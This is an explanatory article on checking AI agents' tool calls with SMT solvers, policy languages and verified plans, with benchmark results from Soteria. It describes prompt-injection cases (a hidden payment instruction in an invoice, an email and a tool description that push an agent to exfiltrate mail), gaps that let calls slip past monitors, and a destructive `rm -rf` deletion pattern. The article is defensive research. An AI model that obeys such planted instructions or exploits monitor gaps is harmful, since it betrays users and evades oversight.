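# Checking AI agents' tool calls with SMT solvers: file paths, secret data and the order of actions

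## What an SMT solver can answer about a tool call

An AI agent is a language model together with ordinary software that carries out the actions the model requests, such as editing a file, running a shell command, sending mail or moving money. A satisfiability modulo theories (SMT) solver is a program that takes a logical formula over numbers, strings and similar data and decides whether any values make it true. Engineers have long used these solvers to find faults in hardware and programs. To apply one to an agent, a developer writes a rule for the agent's actions as a formula. Before an action runs, the solver searches for a way to break the rule.

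### How an agent acts, and how a stranger can steer it

A language model only produces text. To let it act, a developer writes a set of functions, the agent's tools, and puts a description of each into the text that the model receives: its name, its purpose, the arguments it takes. When the model's output contains a request in the agreed format, the software around the model parses the request, runs the function and appends the result to the text. The model then continues from the longer text, perhaps with another request. Each request of this kind is a tool call. One for a bank transfer might look like this:

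```
{"tool": "transfer", "arguments": {"to": "ACME Ltd", "amount": 300}}
```

The money moves when the software runs `transfer`, not when the model emits this line. Before the software runs the call, a separate program called a monitor can inspect it and block it. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026), a consultancy preprint, bases a verification scheme on this chance to block calls. It does not analyze the model's weights, training data or sampling, and it treats the model as an adversary that may request anything. The only fact it needs about the surrounding software is that the software can intercept every tool call before the call reaches a real interface.

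The main reason to assume that an agent may make harmful tool calls is prompt injection, the planting of instructions in data that the agent will read. Anyone who can write a web page, an email or a code comment that the agent later opens can try it. For example, a user may ask an agent to pay an invoice that contains, in white text on a white page, an instruction to send a second payment to another account. The software adds the invoice's text to the same sequence that holds the user's request. The model has no reliable way to keep the two separate, and models sometimes follow the planted instruction. The resulting tool call is well formed, and nothing in its format distinguishes it from one the user wanted.

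Intercepting tool calls does not cover everything an agent can do. A model can reveal a secret in a plain message to the user, without a tool call. An outsider can change the target of a call between its approval and its execution. Metere lists both among the cases that the scheme leaves open. When a call starts a script, the scheme needs a separate analysis of the script's source code to cover what the script does.

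### What the solver does with a formula

SMT extends Boolean satisfiability (SAT), the problem of finding values that make a formula true. A SAT formula combines true/false variables using "and", "or" and "not". Rules about tool calls need more than true/false variables because they involve amounts, paths and records of earlier actions. An SMT formula can include statements such as x + y > 500 where a SAT formula could include only a variable. In SMT, a "theory" is the set of rules that defines what symbols such as + and > mean.

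Early solvers translated everything to bits, so that a 32-bit number became 32 Boolean variables. This works, but even a fact as obvious as x + y = y + x becomes hard to recognise among the bit operations. The predominant design today is what Barrett and Tinelli's *Satisfiability Modulo Theories* calls the lazy approach, in which a SAT solver handles the logical structure and passes the statements about numbers or arrays to one or more theory solvers. The general scheme is called DPLL(T), where T stands for the theory and DPLL for Davis, Putnam, Logemann and Loveland, whose search procedure for Boolean formulas it extends.

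Z3, an open-source solver from Microsoft Research, uses by default a descendant of this scheme that also records the cause of every dead end. Its developers, Bjørner, Eisenhofer and colleagues, in *Z3 Internals (Draft)*, show the mechanism on a small formula:

(x > 0 or y > 0) and x + y < 0

The solver first sets x + y < 0 to true, because the formula requires it. The bracket leaves a choice. Suppose the search sets both x > 0 and y > 0 to true. The Boolean part finds no conflict, because it treats the three comparisons as unrelated true-or-false variables. The arithmetic solver rejects the combination, because two positive numbers cannot have a negative sum. It returns the reason as a new clause, "x > 0 is false or y > 0 is false", which rules out the same mistake in later branches. The search undoes its last choice and sets y > 0 to false. The assignments are now consistent, for instance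 with x = 1 and y = −2. The arithmetic solver can also derive from x + y < 0 and x > 0 that y > 0 is false, before the search tries setting it to true.

Policies, the sets of rules that tool calls must obey, contain many such choices. For example, the rule "a transfer above 300 needs a person's approval" becomes "the amount is at most 300, or a person has approved it". The Boolean search tries the alternatives, and the theory solver checks the amounts within each.

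Three theories besides integers matter for tool calls. The theory of strings applies to file paths and covers joining, length and prefixes. Microsoft's *SMTLIB2 standard Arrays* defines arrays through two operations: `select a i` gives the value at position `i` of the array `a`, and `store a i v` gives a copy of `a` with the value `v` at position `i`. An array whose positions are file names and whose values are true or false can record which files an agent has read so far. Each read adds a `store` that sets the file's value to true, and a check before an edit uses `select` to look that value up.

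The last of the three is the theory of uninterpreted functions. Such a function has no definition, and the solver may assume only that equal inputs give equal outputs. This suits a tool whose inner workings nobody wants to write out as logic, such as a program that redacts documents. That assumption alone can be enough to prove a contradiction, as in an example from Bjørner and colleagues with three statements: a = f(f(a)), a = f(f(f(a))), and a ≠ f(a). Since f(f(a)) equals a, f(f(f(a))) equals f(a). The second statement then implies that a equals f(a), which contradicts the third, so no function f satisfies all three.

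A solver has three possible answers. SMT-LIB (2026), the standard input language for these programs, defines them as follows:

- `sat` (satisfiable): the solver has found values that make all the formulas true together.
- `unsat` (unsatisfiable): the solver has established that no such values exist.
- `unknown`: the search was inconclusive, because of resource limits, because the solver's method is incomplete for formulas of this class, or for some other reason.

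Logicians call a satisfying set of values a "model", which has nothing to do with language models.

The answers differ in how easily anyone can check them. A `sat` answer can be checked by putting the returned values into the formula and calculating. An `unsat` answer covers every possible assignment, usually infinitely many, and depends on the solver's reasoning being correct. An `unknown` answer does not justify allowing the call, and a monitor that allows it anyway has not checked it. How often a solver returns `unknown` depends on the theory. According to course notes from the University of Washington, linear arithmetic over the real numbers can be solved in polynomial time, while arrays and linear arithmetic over the integers are NP-complete, which means that every known method takes exponential time on the worst inputs. For strings, whether the problem is decidable at all depends on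 which operations the formula uses.

### Asking for the case in which a rule fails

A solver looks for one assignment that satisfies a formula, but a safety rule has to hold under every assignment. To prove a rule, one therefore uses proof by refutation, asking the solver for a case in which the rule fails. Microsoft's *Propositional Logic* explains that a formula F is valid, meaning true under every assignment, precisely when "not F" is unsatisfiable.

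For a tool call the query has this general shape:

what is known about the calls **and** what the guards enforce **and not** the rule

To check a rule, we give the solver a description of what is known and the negation of the rule, and ask whether both can hold. The description includes each tool's contract, which states what must hold before the tool runs and what holds afterwards. If the answer is `sat`, the values that come with it are a counterexample, a concrete way to break the rule. If the answer is `unsat`, the description contains no such case. The rule must be negated correctly. The negation of "both transfers are at most 300" is "at least one is above 300". Someone who writes "both are above 300" instead may get `unsat` even though one transfer can exceed 300.

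Suppose an agent may make two transfers, x and y. The transfer tool refuses any single amount above 300, and the bank's rule is that the two together must not exceed 500. Does the limit on single transfers already guarantee the rule? In SMT-LIB's notation, which puts the operator before its arguments, the question reads:

```
(declare-const x Int)                  ; first transfer
(declare-const y Int)                  ; second transfer
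(assert (and (<= 0 x) (<= x 300)))
(assert (and (<= 0 y) (<= y 300)))
(assert (> (+ x y) 500))               ; the rule fails
(check-sat)                            ; sat
(get-model)                            ; for example x = 300, y = 201

(assert (<= (+ x y) 500))              ; the guard
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

Microsoft's *Basic Commands* explains Z3's commands. `declare-const` introduces an unknown of a given type, `assert` adds a formula to a stack, `check-sat` tests whether all the formulas on the stack can be true at once, and `get-model` prints values that make them true. Z3 also has a Python interface, so a monitor written in Python can build the same query directly.

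The solver first returns `sat`, because a transfer of 300 followed by one of 201 keeps each transfer within its own limit but exceeds the total limit of 500 by 1. It could also return 300 and 300, since a plain satisfiability check may return any solution, not necessarily the smallest or most instructive. The next step is to add a guard, a check in the monitor that refuses the second transfer if the total would exceed 500. With the guard in the formula, the solver returns `unsat`.

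This proof is easy because the guard directly contradicts the violation. The solver needs arithmetic if the bank instead drops the check on the total and lowers the single limit from 300 to 250. The violation is then the only assertion that refers to a total of 500, but the answer is still `unsat`, because adding x ≤ 250 and y ≤ 250 gives x + y ≤ 500, which rules out x + y > 500.

When the assertions contradict each other, a solver can also use the SMT-LIB command `get-unsat-core` to return a subset of them that is contradictory by itself. In the version with the guard on the total, the guard and the violation contradict each other without the limits of 300. In the version with the lower limits, the core must contain both limits. An engineer can see from the core which checks the system's safety depends on, and so which ones to keep.

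The `unsat` result covers only what the formula describes, which is two transfers in whole units of one currency. It doesn't cover a third transfer of 100, or a payment in cents if the variables stand for whole euros. Asserting the guard in the formula also doesn't enforce it in the bank's software. If a programmer types 5000 instead of 500 in the monitor itself, the solver still returns `unsat` because the formula hasn't changed, but the transfers go through.

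An `unsat` result doesn't show that the rule holds if the assumptions contradict one another. No assignment satisfies such assumptions, so the solver returns `unsat` for every query, including whether the rule can fail. These contradictions can be hard to spot. SMT-LIB warns that its syntax permits a recursive definition in which f(x) equals "not f(x)", which alone makes the whole set of formulas unsatisfiable. An easy check is to run `check-sat` on the assumptions before adding the violation, which should return `sat`. An unsatisfiable core that leaves out the violation is another warning sign.

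A single call whose arguments are all known doesn't need a solver. If the agent has sent 300 and now requests 150, an ordinary if-statement can check the total of 450. A solver becomes useful when some values are unknown, such as the arguments of a later step or the contents of a file nobody has read yet, or when we want to know whether a guard suffices for every amount an agent might request.

### Tests and second models

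The usual way to gain confidence in a guard is to test it. With whole amounts from 0 to 300, there are 90,601 possible pairs of transfers, and 5,050 of them, about one in eighteen, total more than 500. Fifty random tests would hit at least one such pair with a probability of about 94 percent. If the cap on the total is raised to 599, only one pair, 300 and 300, breaks the rule, and a thousand random tests have roughly a 1 percent chance of finding it. The solver's query changes by only one number. A good tester would catch this case by trying the maximum values first, but choosing the right test is harder when a violation depends on a combination of a path, an approval flag and the order of six earlier calls.

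A program can try every case when there are few of them. Metere's preprint presents its method as an SMT search, but the checker released with it enumerates sequences of calls exhaustively. With ten permitted kinds of action and eight calls, that means 11^8 sequences, about 214 million, which a computer can manage. The preprint also gives about 100 as the typical number of calls between two run-time checks. That would mean 11^100 sequences, a number with 105 digits, which is far too many to enumerate. An SMT solver can rule out a huge family of sequences with one learned clause, though there is no general guarantee that it will.

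Unlike a solver, a test runs the real transfer tool and monitor, so it can expose the mistyped 5000 that the formula leaves out. Teams that use a solver still need tests, above all to check that the tools behave as their contracts describe.

Another common safeguard is a second language model that judges each proposed call, usually with the surrounding conversation as context. It can handle questions that nobody has a formula for, such as whether a payment is plausibly what the user wanted or whether an email is insulting. But its verdict covers only that one call, may differ on a second run, and includes no counterexample that a person could check by calculation. If the judge also reads the invoice, the planted instruction reaches it too.

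Text from the invoice can enter the formula only as a string value, so the solver treats a command to send money like any other sequence of characters. The monitor must quote that text properly. If it pastes raw text into an SMT-LIB script, an attacker could add their own assertions. Solvers may use randomness internally, so two runs can produce different counterexamples, but a correct solver cannot return `sat` on one run and `unsat` on another for the same formula.

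The query about transfers contains only two numbers and a cap, so the planted text can't influence the solver, but the solver also can't check a transfer against the user's wishes. The query leaves out the payee, the invoice and what the user asked for. If the agent pays the invoice with 300 and then follows the hidden instruction to send 150 to the attacker, the total is 450 and the rule still holds. A rule that payees must be on an approved list would stop the second transfer, but only if someone had thought to write it and had included the payee in the formula.

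## Choosing when to check: each call, the whole plan, or the policy itself

Under the bank's rule, an agent's two transfers must not exceed 500 in total. A developer can check this rule at three points. A monitor can wait for each transfer, add its amount to what the agent has already sent, and check the total against the limit. If the agent first writes a plan, meaning a sequence or graph of tool calls fixed before any of them runs, a verifier can check both transfers before any money moves. The bank can also analyse the policy without running an agent, to see whether it allows any request that it should refuse.

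| | Monitor on each call | Verification of a plan | Analysis of the policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| When it runs | Before every tool call | After planning, before the first call | When someone writes or changes a rule |
| What it examines | Actual arguments, and earlier calls if the monitor keeps a record | Every branch of one plan, with tool results still unknown | Every request that the policy language can describe |
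| Main cost | A trustworthy record of past calls | Model tokens for writing and repairing plans, plus solver time | A policy language limited enough to analyse |
| What it misses | Steps the agent has yet to take | Departures from the plan | What an agent will actually request |

### A monitor on each call

When a tool call reaches the monitor, the model has already filled in every argument, so the monitor needs no solver. AWS, Amazon's cloud division, offers such a monitor as part of AgentCore, its platform for running agents. Tool calls pass through a gateway that blocks every call unless the customer's policy permits it. AWS fully released the monitor on 3 March 2026, according to its *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026).

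Customers write the policy in Cedar, an open-source language from AWS. A call goes through only if at least one rule permits it and none forbids it. An example in AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* permits a bulk discount for customers in the "Platinum" tier who order at least 50 items, unless the order contains limited-edition or seasonal products. The tier comes from the user's login token, which the model cannot alter, but the model supplies the quantity in its tool call. The gateway will therefore refuse a call for a discount on 40 items, whatever led the model to make it, but if the model writes 50 when the customer ordered 40, the call meets the 50-item minimum.

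Cedar has no loops and keeps no state, so evaluation is fast and identical requests always get identical answers. Without state, it cannot express the bank's total, because whether to allow a transfer of 201 depends on whether 300 has already gone out. In the summer of 2026, AWS released a second language, Dogwood, which extends Cedar with conditions on earlier events. A rule in AWS's *Temporal policies* permits an agent to sell shares only if someone approved a sale of the same number of shares in the same stock within the previous hour. Other Dogwood operators count earlier calls or add up their amounts.

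Rules about history are easy to get wrong. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) gives an example in which transfers are capped at $5,000 and an agent requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment. If the rule adds up completed transfers, the total is still zero when each request arrives, so all three go through. If one word is changed so that the rule adds up requested transfers, the third request brings the total to $6,000 and the gateway denies it.

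AgentCore records events separately for each session, and the caller supplies the session's identifier. AWS warns that a new session starts a new count, so a limit of five calls per session does not cap the total for a caller who can open unlimited sessions. If the software that runs the agent picks the identifier, the model must not be able to influence the choice.

Even with a perfect record, a monitor can block the second half of a task after allowing the first. Suppose an agent cancels a customer's flight to rebook it, and the monitor then blocks the new booking because the payment card is not in the customer's profile. The customer is left without a flight even though both of the monitor's decisions followed the rules.

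### Analysing the policy for every possible request

Cedar's restrictions make it possible to check a policy without running an agent. A tool called Cedar Analysis translates the policy's rules into logical formulas and searches for mistakes. AWS gives the example of a refund rule that can never permit anything because it requires the customer's tier to be both "Gold" and "Platinum", where its author meant "or". Another rule applies when the quantity is at least 100 or below 100, which covers every order. The analysis also compares rules with each other. If one rule permits refunds below $100 for Gold customers and another forbids refunds below $500 for Gold and Platinum customers, the permission has no effect because the prohibition overrides it.

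AgentCore runs these checks when a customer attaches a policy to a gateway, and the operation fails if they find an error. It also runs them when a language model drafts Cedar rules from a plain English description, and uses the errors to guide the next draft. AWS says this loop significantly improves the accuracy of the drafts, but gives no figure.

The most useful question for a team that maintains a policy is whether a new version allows anything the old one refused. In one of AWS's examples, the old rule permits a bulk discount on 50 items or more unless the order contains limited-edition products. The new rule makes the exception apply only if the order also exceeds 200 items. Someone skimming the change sees an added condition and may take it for a tightening. Simplified to one quantity and one true/false variable, the comparison looks like this in SMT-LIB, where `define-fun` names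 a formula and `push` and `pop` save and restore the stack of assertions:

```
(declare-const qty Int)
(declare-const limited Bool)          ; order has limited-edition items
(define-fun old-allows () Bool
  (and (>= qty 50) (not limited)))
(define-fun new-allows () Bool
  (and (>= qty 50) (not (and limited (> qty 200)))))

(push)
(assert (and new-allows (not old-allows)))
(check-sat)                           ; sat: e.g. qty = 73, limited = true
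(pop)
(assert (and old-allows (not new-allows)))
(check-sat)                           ; unsat
```

The `sat` answer includes an example of a request that only the new rule allows, an order of 73 limited-edition items. The solver could have returned any quantity from 50 to 200. The `unsat` answer shows that the new rule still allows everything the old rule allowed. Together, the two answers show that the new policy is strictly more permissive. If both answers had been `unsat`, the two versions would allow exactly the same requests.

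A person must still decide whether the bank or shop wants the extra permission. The comparison also treats requests one at a time. InfoQ reports that Dogwood's conditions on history do not work with Cedar's analysis tools, which is why AWS says it created a separate language instead of extending Cedar. An AWS customer therefore cannot use the tools to compare a policy set with its predecessor if the set includes a rule that limits the running total. Analysing the approval rule for share sales would mean covering every possible history as well as every possible request.

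### Meijer's proposal: fix the plan before the data arrives

A plan lies between a single call and the policy itself. It contains several calls in order, so a verifier can check rules about sequences, and it is finite, so the verifier does not have to consider every possible history. Erik Meijer proposed making this check compulsory in *Guardians of the Agents* (2025). The model generates a plan, a verifier checks it against a policy, and ordinary software executes the plan only if it passes.

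In Meijer's example, a user named Michelle asks an agent, "Can you fetch and summarize my emails?" The agent has one tool that fetches mail and another that sends it. One message, from an outsider, claims that legal compliance requires an external backup and tells the assistant to send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address without asking for confirmation or mentioning it. An agent that picks its next call after reading the mail may obey. Michelle then receives a summary that omits the malicious message, and the attacker receives a copy.

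In Meijer's design, the model writes the whole plan from Michelle's request and the tool descriptions before any tool fetches the emails. The plan has three steps: fetch the emails, summarise them, and return the summary. It refers to the emails only as `emails_fetched`, which the executing software later replaces with the real messages. Since that software runs only the steps in the plan, text in an email cannot add a fourth step. A language model still reads the messages to summarise them, so planted text can distort the summary, but the summarising step has no access to the tool that sends mail.

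An attacker can act earlier, by planting instructions in text that the model reads while planning. Meijer gives the example of a tool description that instructs the model to forward all emails whenever it fetches them. The resulting plan would include a step that sends the emails, which the verifier has to catch. The policy defines the fetching tool as a source and the body of an outgoing email as a sink, which data from the source must not reach when the recipient is outside the company. The verifier rejects the plan if it finds a route from source to sink. Meijer suggests finding such routes with CodeQL or Semgrep, existing programs for analysing source code. For checking a plan's effects, such as whether a request to delete two files would also delete others, Meijer suggests Z3 or the program verifier Dafny.

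Meijer argues that a monitor acts too late because the agent has already retrieved and processed private mail by the time the monitor blocks the outgoing message. The argument is weak in this example, since Michelle asked the agent to read her mail and blocking the sending call before it runs prevents the leak. The case for checking the whole plan first is stronger when several actions belong together, as with the cancelled flight, where a verifier can reject the plan before the customer loses the seat.

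Some requests can't be fully planned in advance. If Michelle asks the agent to do whatever her accountant's latest email requests, no one can write the steps before reading the email. A plan can branch on results, but only into branches the model wrote in advance. Meijer acknowledges that nobody had formally measured how planning first affects an agent's ability to answer requests, and points to signs that models reason better when they write out a program. The article reports no measurements of tasks completed or attacks stopped.

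### Two prototypes, and who writes the policy

Two experimental programs carry out this kind of check with Z3. One is metareflection/guardians, an open-source implementation of Meijer's proposal. clauz3's *Background And Related Work* describes it as a verifier for structured plans that combines rules about data moving from source to sink, security automata, and Z3 checks of what holds before and after each tool runs. A security automaton is a state machine that reads the sequence of calls and rejects it on reaching an error state. Meijer presented the automaton as a run-time monitor, and guardians also evaluates it on the plan. The operator, who deploys the agent, writes the policy without the agent's input.

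The other program, clauz3, has the agent write a short Python script and attach guarantees about its effects, for example that it will send email only to bob@example.com and at most once. The prover checks the guarantees on every branch, and the user then approves or rejects them without having to read the code. In another example, a user wants the agent to pay a bill, up to $500. The script looks up the outstanding balance and pays the smaller of the balance and $500. The balance isn't known when the check runs, so the prover treats it as an unknown number, looks for a value that would make the payment exceed $500, and proves that there is none.

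clauz3 relies on a small library of human-audited tools. Each call to one of these tools produces a record with the tool's name, its arguments and the condition under which the program reaches the call. A guarantee is a statement about all these records. For example, "only Bob" becomes "every email record has Bob's address", and Z3 searches for a branch on which an email record has a different address. If a description in the audited library is wrong, the proof will contain the same error.

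clauz3 and guardians would treat Michelle's attacker differently. According to clauz3's *Guardians Synergies*, its prover would reject a program that forwards mail to an outside address if the guarantees allow only company addresses. But clauz3 does not track where a value came from, so the guarantees cannot forbid putting the mailbox's contents in an email to a permitted colleague. It also keeps its records as an unordered set, which makes rules such as "approval before transfer" hard to express. A separate mechanism supports rules about the final state, such as requiring every door to be locked at the end. guardians handles both the origin of data and the order of calls.

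Who writes the policy matters most when someone has manipulated the agent. Under guardians, a manipulated agent cannot weaken the rules. Under clauz3, it can propose a program with weak guarantees, or one that explicitly guarantees nothing about email, and the proof will succeed. According to clauz3's *FAQ*, the tool does not prevent prompt injection, but users can see the weak guarantees before they approve the program. This protects only users who read the guarantees, and Meijer notes that people who face constant consent requests begin to click "Allow" without reading. Asking once per program instead of once per call should help, though neither project has published a test with users. An organisation can also mark certain guarantees as required, and clauz3 then rejects any program that does not meet them, so the operator can set part of the policy.

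### How Soteria verifies a plan

In *SOTERIA*, He, Desai and colleagues (2026) at Princeton University and the data company Snowflake built and measured a system that uses both plans and monitors. A language model first translates a company's written policy into formulas and each tool's description into a contract, which people then check and correct. For every task, another model, the planner, writes a plan.

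Soteria represents the plan as a guarded transition system. This is a graph whose nodes are states, or stages of the task, and whose edges are transitions, each with at most one action such as a tool call. A guard on a transition is a condition that must hold before the transition can fire. Here is a plan for cancelling an airline reservation, adapted from the paper:

```
LOOKUP        resv = Get-Resv(rid)               -> CHECK_AGE
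CHECK_AGE     hrs = Hours-Diff(resv.ts, time)    -> CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES   if hrs <= 24                       -> DO_CANCEL
              otherwise                          -> NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL     Cancel-Resv(rid, reason)           -> DONE
```

The airline's policy permits cancellation within 24 hours of booking, and the plan meets this condition. The policy also requires the agent to first use a tool called No-Flown to check that the customer has not flown any part of the trip, but the plan omits this step.

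To find such errors without running anything, Soteria computes a formula for each state, called the symbolic state Σ(s), that describes every situation in which the plan could reach that state. For each transition, Soteria takes the formula of the state the transition leaves and adds the transition's guard and the postcondition of the tool it calls. When two transitions lead to the same state, Soteria joins their formulas with "or". At CHECK_RULES the formula contains the postconditions of Get-Resv and Hours-Diff. At DO_CANCEL it also contains hrs ≤ 24. The number of hours remains unknown throughout, so one formula covers all reservations.

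From these formulas Soteria generates verification conditions, statements that must be true if the plan is correct. For a call to a tool *a* with precondition P, from a state *s* under guard *g*, the condition is

Σ(s) ∧ g ⇒ P

The conditions that hold when the plan makes the call must guarantee that the tool's requirements are met. A solver proves this by showing that no values satisfy Σ(s) and *g* but not P.

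Two more conditions ensure that the plan cannot get stuck. First, Σ(s) must be satisfiable at every state before the end, or no execution can reach that state. This check also catches contracts that contradict one another. Second, at each branch, Σ(s) must imply that at least one guard is true. If the planner had written "hrs < 24" on one branch and "hrs > 24" on the other, a solver would return hrs = 24 as a counterexample, a reservation for which the plan has no next step.

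Checking a rule about earlier calls requires a record of those calls. Soteria adds this record to the verification as extra variables that have no role in the real execution: a step counter, a log for each tool that some rule mentions, and a map of which tool results contributed to each variable. The flown-flight rule then requires that, for every entry in the log of cancellations, the log of No-Flown contains an entry with a lower step number, the same reservation and the result "true". This must hold wherever the plan can end.

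In the plan above, the path to DONE leaves one entry in the log of cancellations and none in the other log, so the check fails. Adding a call to No-Flown just before the cancellation would not fix this, because the tool may return "false" and the solver would find the run where the plan cancels anyway. The planner also has to add a guard that prevents the cancellation when the result is "false".

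Soteria writes all these conditions in Dafny, a programming language whose built-in verifier uses Z3. The time limit is 10 seconds per state. When a condition fails, the planner receives a description of the failure and tries again, up to eight times in the main experiments. If no plan passes every check, Soteria continues with the one that passed the most.

Complete plans for long tasks are hard to write correctly, so Soteria keeps a library of sub-plans for standard procedures such as cancellation or refund. It verifies each sub-plan separately, and a larger plan can then use it like a tool, relying only on its contract. With GPT-5.4-mini on the airline tasks, 65 of 68 planning attempts ended in a verified plan when sub-plans were used, compared with 38 of 60 without them.

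The proofs assume that each tool behaves as its contract states. The plan must also contain no cycles, because Soteria's encoding needs a finite order of states. A proof covers only executions that follow the plan, and Soteria doesn't normally force the agent to follow it. The model that carries out the task receives the plan as a flowchart of remaining steps, but can call any tool. A stricter mode blocks every call outside the plan, including harmless ones. If a customer asks to cancel one reservation and look up another, the strict mode can refuse the lookup because the cancellation plan has no such step.

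In the normal mode, a monitor checks each proposed call. It appends the call to the record of what the agent has done and checks the updated record against the rules. All the values are known by then, so it evaluates the rules directly, without calling Z3. If the monitor blocks a cancellation because No-Flown is missing, it reports the missing step, and the agent can make that call and try again. The monitor and the verifier use the same rules, but the monitor also works when an agent ignores its plan. After each call, it compares the tool's result with the postcondition and aborts the task if they disagree, because the proof relied on that postcondition. Some rules require a later action, such as reading a file back after writing it, and the monitor can only check these when the task ends.

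### What the measurements favour

He and colleagues ran Soteria on 207 tasks from three benchmarks with four language models. In 50 tasks from τ²-Airline and 114 from τ²-Retail, the agent serves a simulated customer. The other 43, from Toolathlon, involve files, terminals and documents. They compared Soteria with three other safeguards and with an agent that had the policy only in its instructions. The other safeguards were NeMo Guardrails, where a second language model judges each call, and two run-time monitors, AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts.

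A task counted as a success only if the agent completed it without breaking any rule. This differs from the benchmarks' own scoring. In one airline task, the unguarded GPT-5.4-mini upgraded a reservation to business class so that it would qualify for cancellation, then cancelled it without checking whether any segments had already been flown, and the benchmark gave it full credit. The table shows the success rates for the best of the four alternatives and for Soteria.

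| Model | Airline: best alternative | Airline: Soteria | Retail: best alternative | Retail: Soteria | Toolathlon: best alternative | Toolathlon: Soteria |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 50.0 | 60.0 | 20.2 | 35.1 | 2.3 | 11.6 |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 36.0 | 62.0 | 38.6 | 45.6 | 2.3 | 16.3 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 30.0 | 70.0 | 31.6 | 56.1 | 4.7 | 9.3 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 56.0 | 88.0 | 46.5 | 90.4 | 11.6 | 18.6 |

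Soteria had no rule violations in any of the twelve combinations, while every alternative had some in each. But the largest gains have little to do with violations. The unguarded Opus 4.6 completed only 53.5 percent of the retail tasks even when violations were not counted against it, so preventing them alone could not have brought it near 90 percent. He et al. found that it often collected all the necessary information and then transferred the customer to a human. It made the expected change to an order in only 57 percent of the tasks that required one, but in all of them when it was given a plan that named the change.

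These figures come from one attempt per task. The team also ran GPT-5.4-mini five times on the airline tasks, with three planning retries instead of eight to save money. Soteria's average success rate was 50.8 percent and AgentSpec's was 48.0 percent, with overlapping confidence intervals. With this model, Soteria's advantage over an ordinary monitor in completed tasks may be small or absent. The difference in violations persisted, with none in any Soteria run and an average of 4.4 per AgentSpec run.

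To separate the effects of the components, He and colleagues added them one at a time on the airline tasks:

| Components | GPT-5.4-mini: violations | GPT-5.4-mini: success | Gemini 3 Flash: violations | Gemini 3 Flash: success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 13 | 44% | 27 | 32% |
| With plan verification | 10 | 46% | 24 | 32% |
| With sub-plans as well | 12 | 50% | 22 | 38% |
| With the monitor as well | 0 | 60% | 0 | 62% |

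Verification alone cut violations with GPT-5.4-mini from 13 to 10. That could be chance, since the unguarded agent's count varied between repeated runs with a standard deviation of about four. Only the monitor brought the number to zero. Verification alone probably didn't prevent all violations because the agent didn't follow its plans. Nearly all plans passed verification once sub-plans were available, yet 12 violations remained.

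These results support choosing the monitor if a team can implement only one of the two. Plan verification is worth adding where a half-finished task does damage, or where the agent tends to give up. It is less certain how much it adds to a good monitor, because the experiment did not test Soteria's monitor without a plan. Policy analysis was not part of the comparison, but it checks the policy itself, which neither of the others does, so a team whose rules fit a language like Cedar has little reason to leave it out.

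Planning also costs money. In the conversational benchmarks, Soteria writes a new plan at each turn, and an airline task with Opus 4.6 cost about 80 cents, compared with 32 to 34 cents for the alternatives. With GPT-5.4-mini, the same kind of task cost 12.5 cents, compared with between 3 and 4 cents. Toolathlon tasks need only one plan, and with Opus 4.6 Soteria cost 43 cents per task, compared with 90 cents or more for the alternatives.

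On Toolathlon, however, the two Claude models finished fewer tasks with Soteria than with any alternative, if tasks finished with violations are counted. Opus 4.6 completed 8 of the 43 tasks with Soteria and 13 without any safeguard, and Haiku 4.5 completed 4 with Soteria and between 6 and 9 with the alternatives. GPT-5.4-mini and Gemini 3 Flash completed as many with Soteria as with their best alternative. Soteria leads in the table only because most of the completions with the alternatives broke a rule. In many of those violations, the agent wrote a file without first listing the directory or without reading the file back afterwards. A user who cares mainly about the finished file may not count that as failure.

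The obedience score depends on the formulas that He and colleagues wrote: 24 for the airline, 33 for the shop and 41 for Toolathlon. Soteria's monitor enforces the same formulas that the evaluation uses, so a count of zero violations shows that the enforcement works, but not whether the formulas capture the written policy. The team corrected some wrongly encoded formulas and added missing ones while auditing the results. At least one remaining formula is too narrow: the rule against destructive deletion in the terminal matches only four spellings, including `rm -rf`. The command `rm -r -f data` also deletes a directory but contains none of the four, so it would count as obedient.

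## Turning a written rule into a formula

Companies write their policies in prose, which someone has to translate into formulas before a solver can use it. For Soteria, the translation took He and colleagues a few hours per benchmark, mostly spent reading the policy and checking formulas that a language model had drafted. The work has five steps: list the facts the checker can observe, give each a type, write a contract for each tool, write the rule, and test the rule on calls that must pass and calls that must fail. The main example here is a rule that a customer may cancel a booking within 24 hours of making it. Some requirements, such as that the agent be polite, may be impossible to write as a formula.

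### Facts, types and contracts

The cancellation rule depends on when the customer booked and when the agent requests the cancellation. The checker can read the booking time from the reservation system and the request time from its own clock. It shouldn't take either from the agent's account of the conversation, because a planted instruction can lead the model to report a false time. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) describes a monitor that records facts only from tool results and the user's own messages. If the agent writes that the user has approved a transfer, the record doesn't change.

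A fact that has no variable in the formula cannot affect the answer. AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks concepts* gives the example of a student who claims the right to hand in homework late because of "a fake doctor's note". If the policy has no variable for whether the note is fake, the check may approve the claim.

Giving a variable the wrong type can change the rule. If the variable for a booking's age holds whole hours and the software rounds down, a booking made 24 hours and 40 minutes ago counts as 24 hours old and still qualifies. Storing the age as a real number avoids this. Units cause similar errors. AWS's *Automated Reasoning policy best practices* warns that "2 years" may end up as 2 in a variable that counts months. Numeric variables also need ranges, or the solver will allow bookings made in the future. A variable with a fixed list of categories works only if no two categories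 can apply at once. A shop that gives each customer one type, "veteran" or "teacher", cannot describe a veteran who teaches.

The next step is to add the tools' contracts. The cancellation tool's precondition might be that the reservation exists and is active, and its postcondition that it is cancelled. To check several calls in a row, the formula needs a separate copy of the state for each step. *MANTRA* (2026), which describes a method for generating agent benchmarks, uses this scheme. If the agent calls a tool at step i, the tool's precondition must hold in state i, and its postcondition constrains state i + 1.

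A postcondition must also state what the tool leaves unchanged. If the contract specifies only that reservation 17 is now cancelled, the solver also allows outcomes in which reservation 18 has vanished. The missing statement, that everything else stays the same, is called a frame condition.

Meijer illustrates the problem with an agent that has to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The deletion tool accepts patterns, so the model writes a plan that deletes `*.txt` in a single call. If the request's postcondition requires only that the two files no longer exist, the plan satisfies it, even though it also deletes every other text file. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes called this kind of difficulty the frame problem in 1969.

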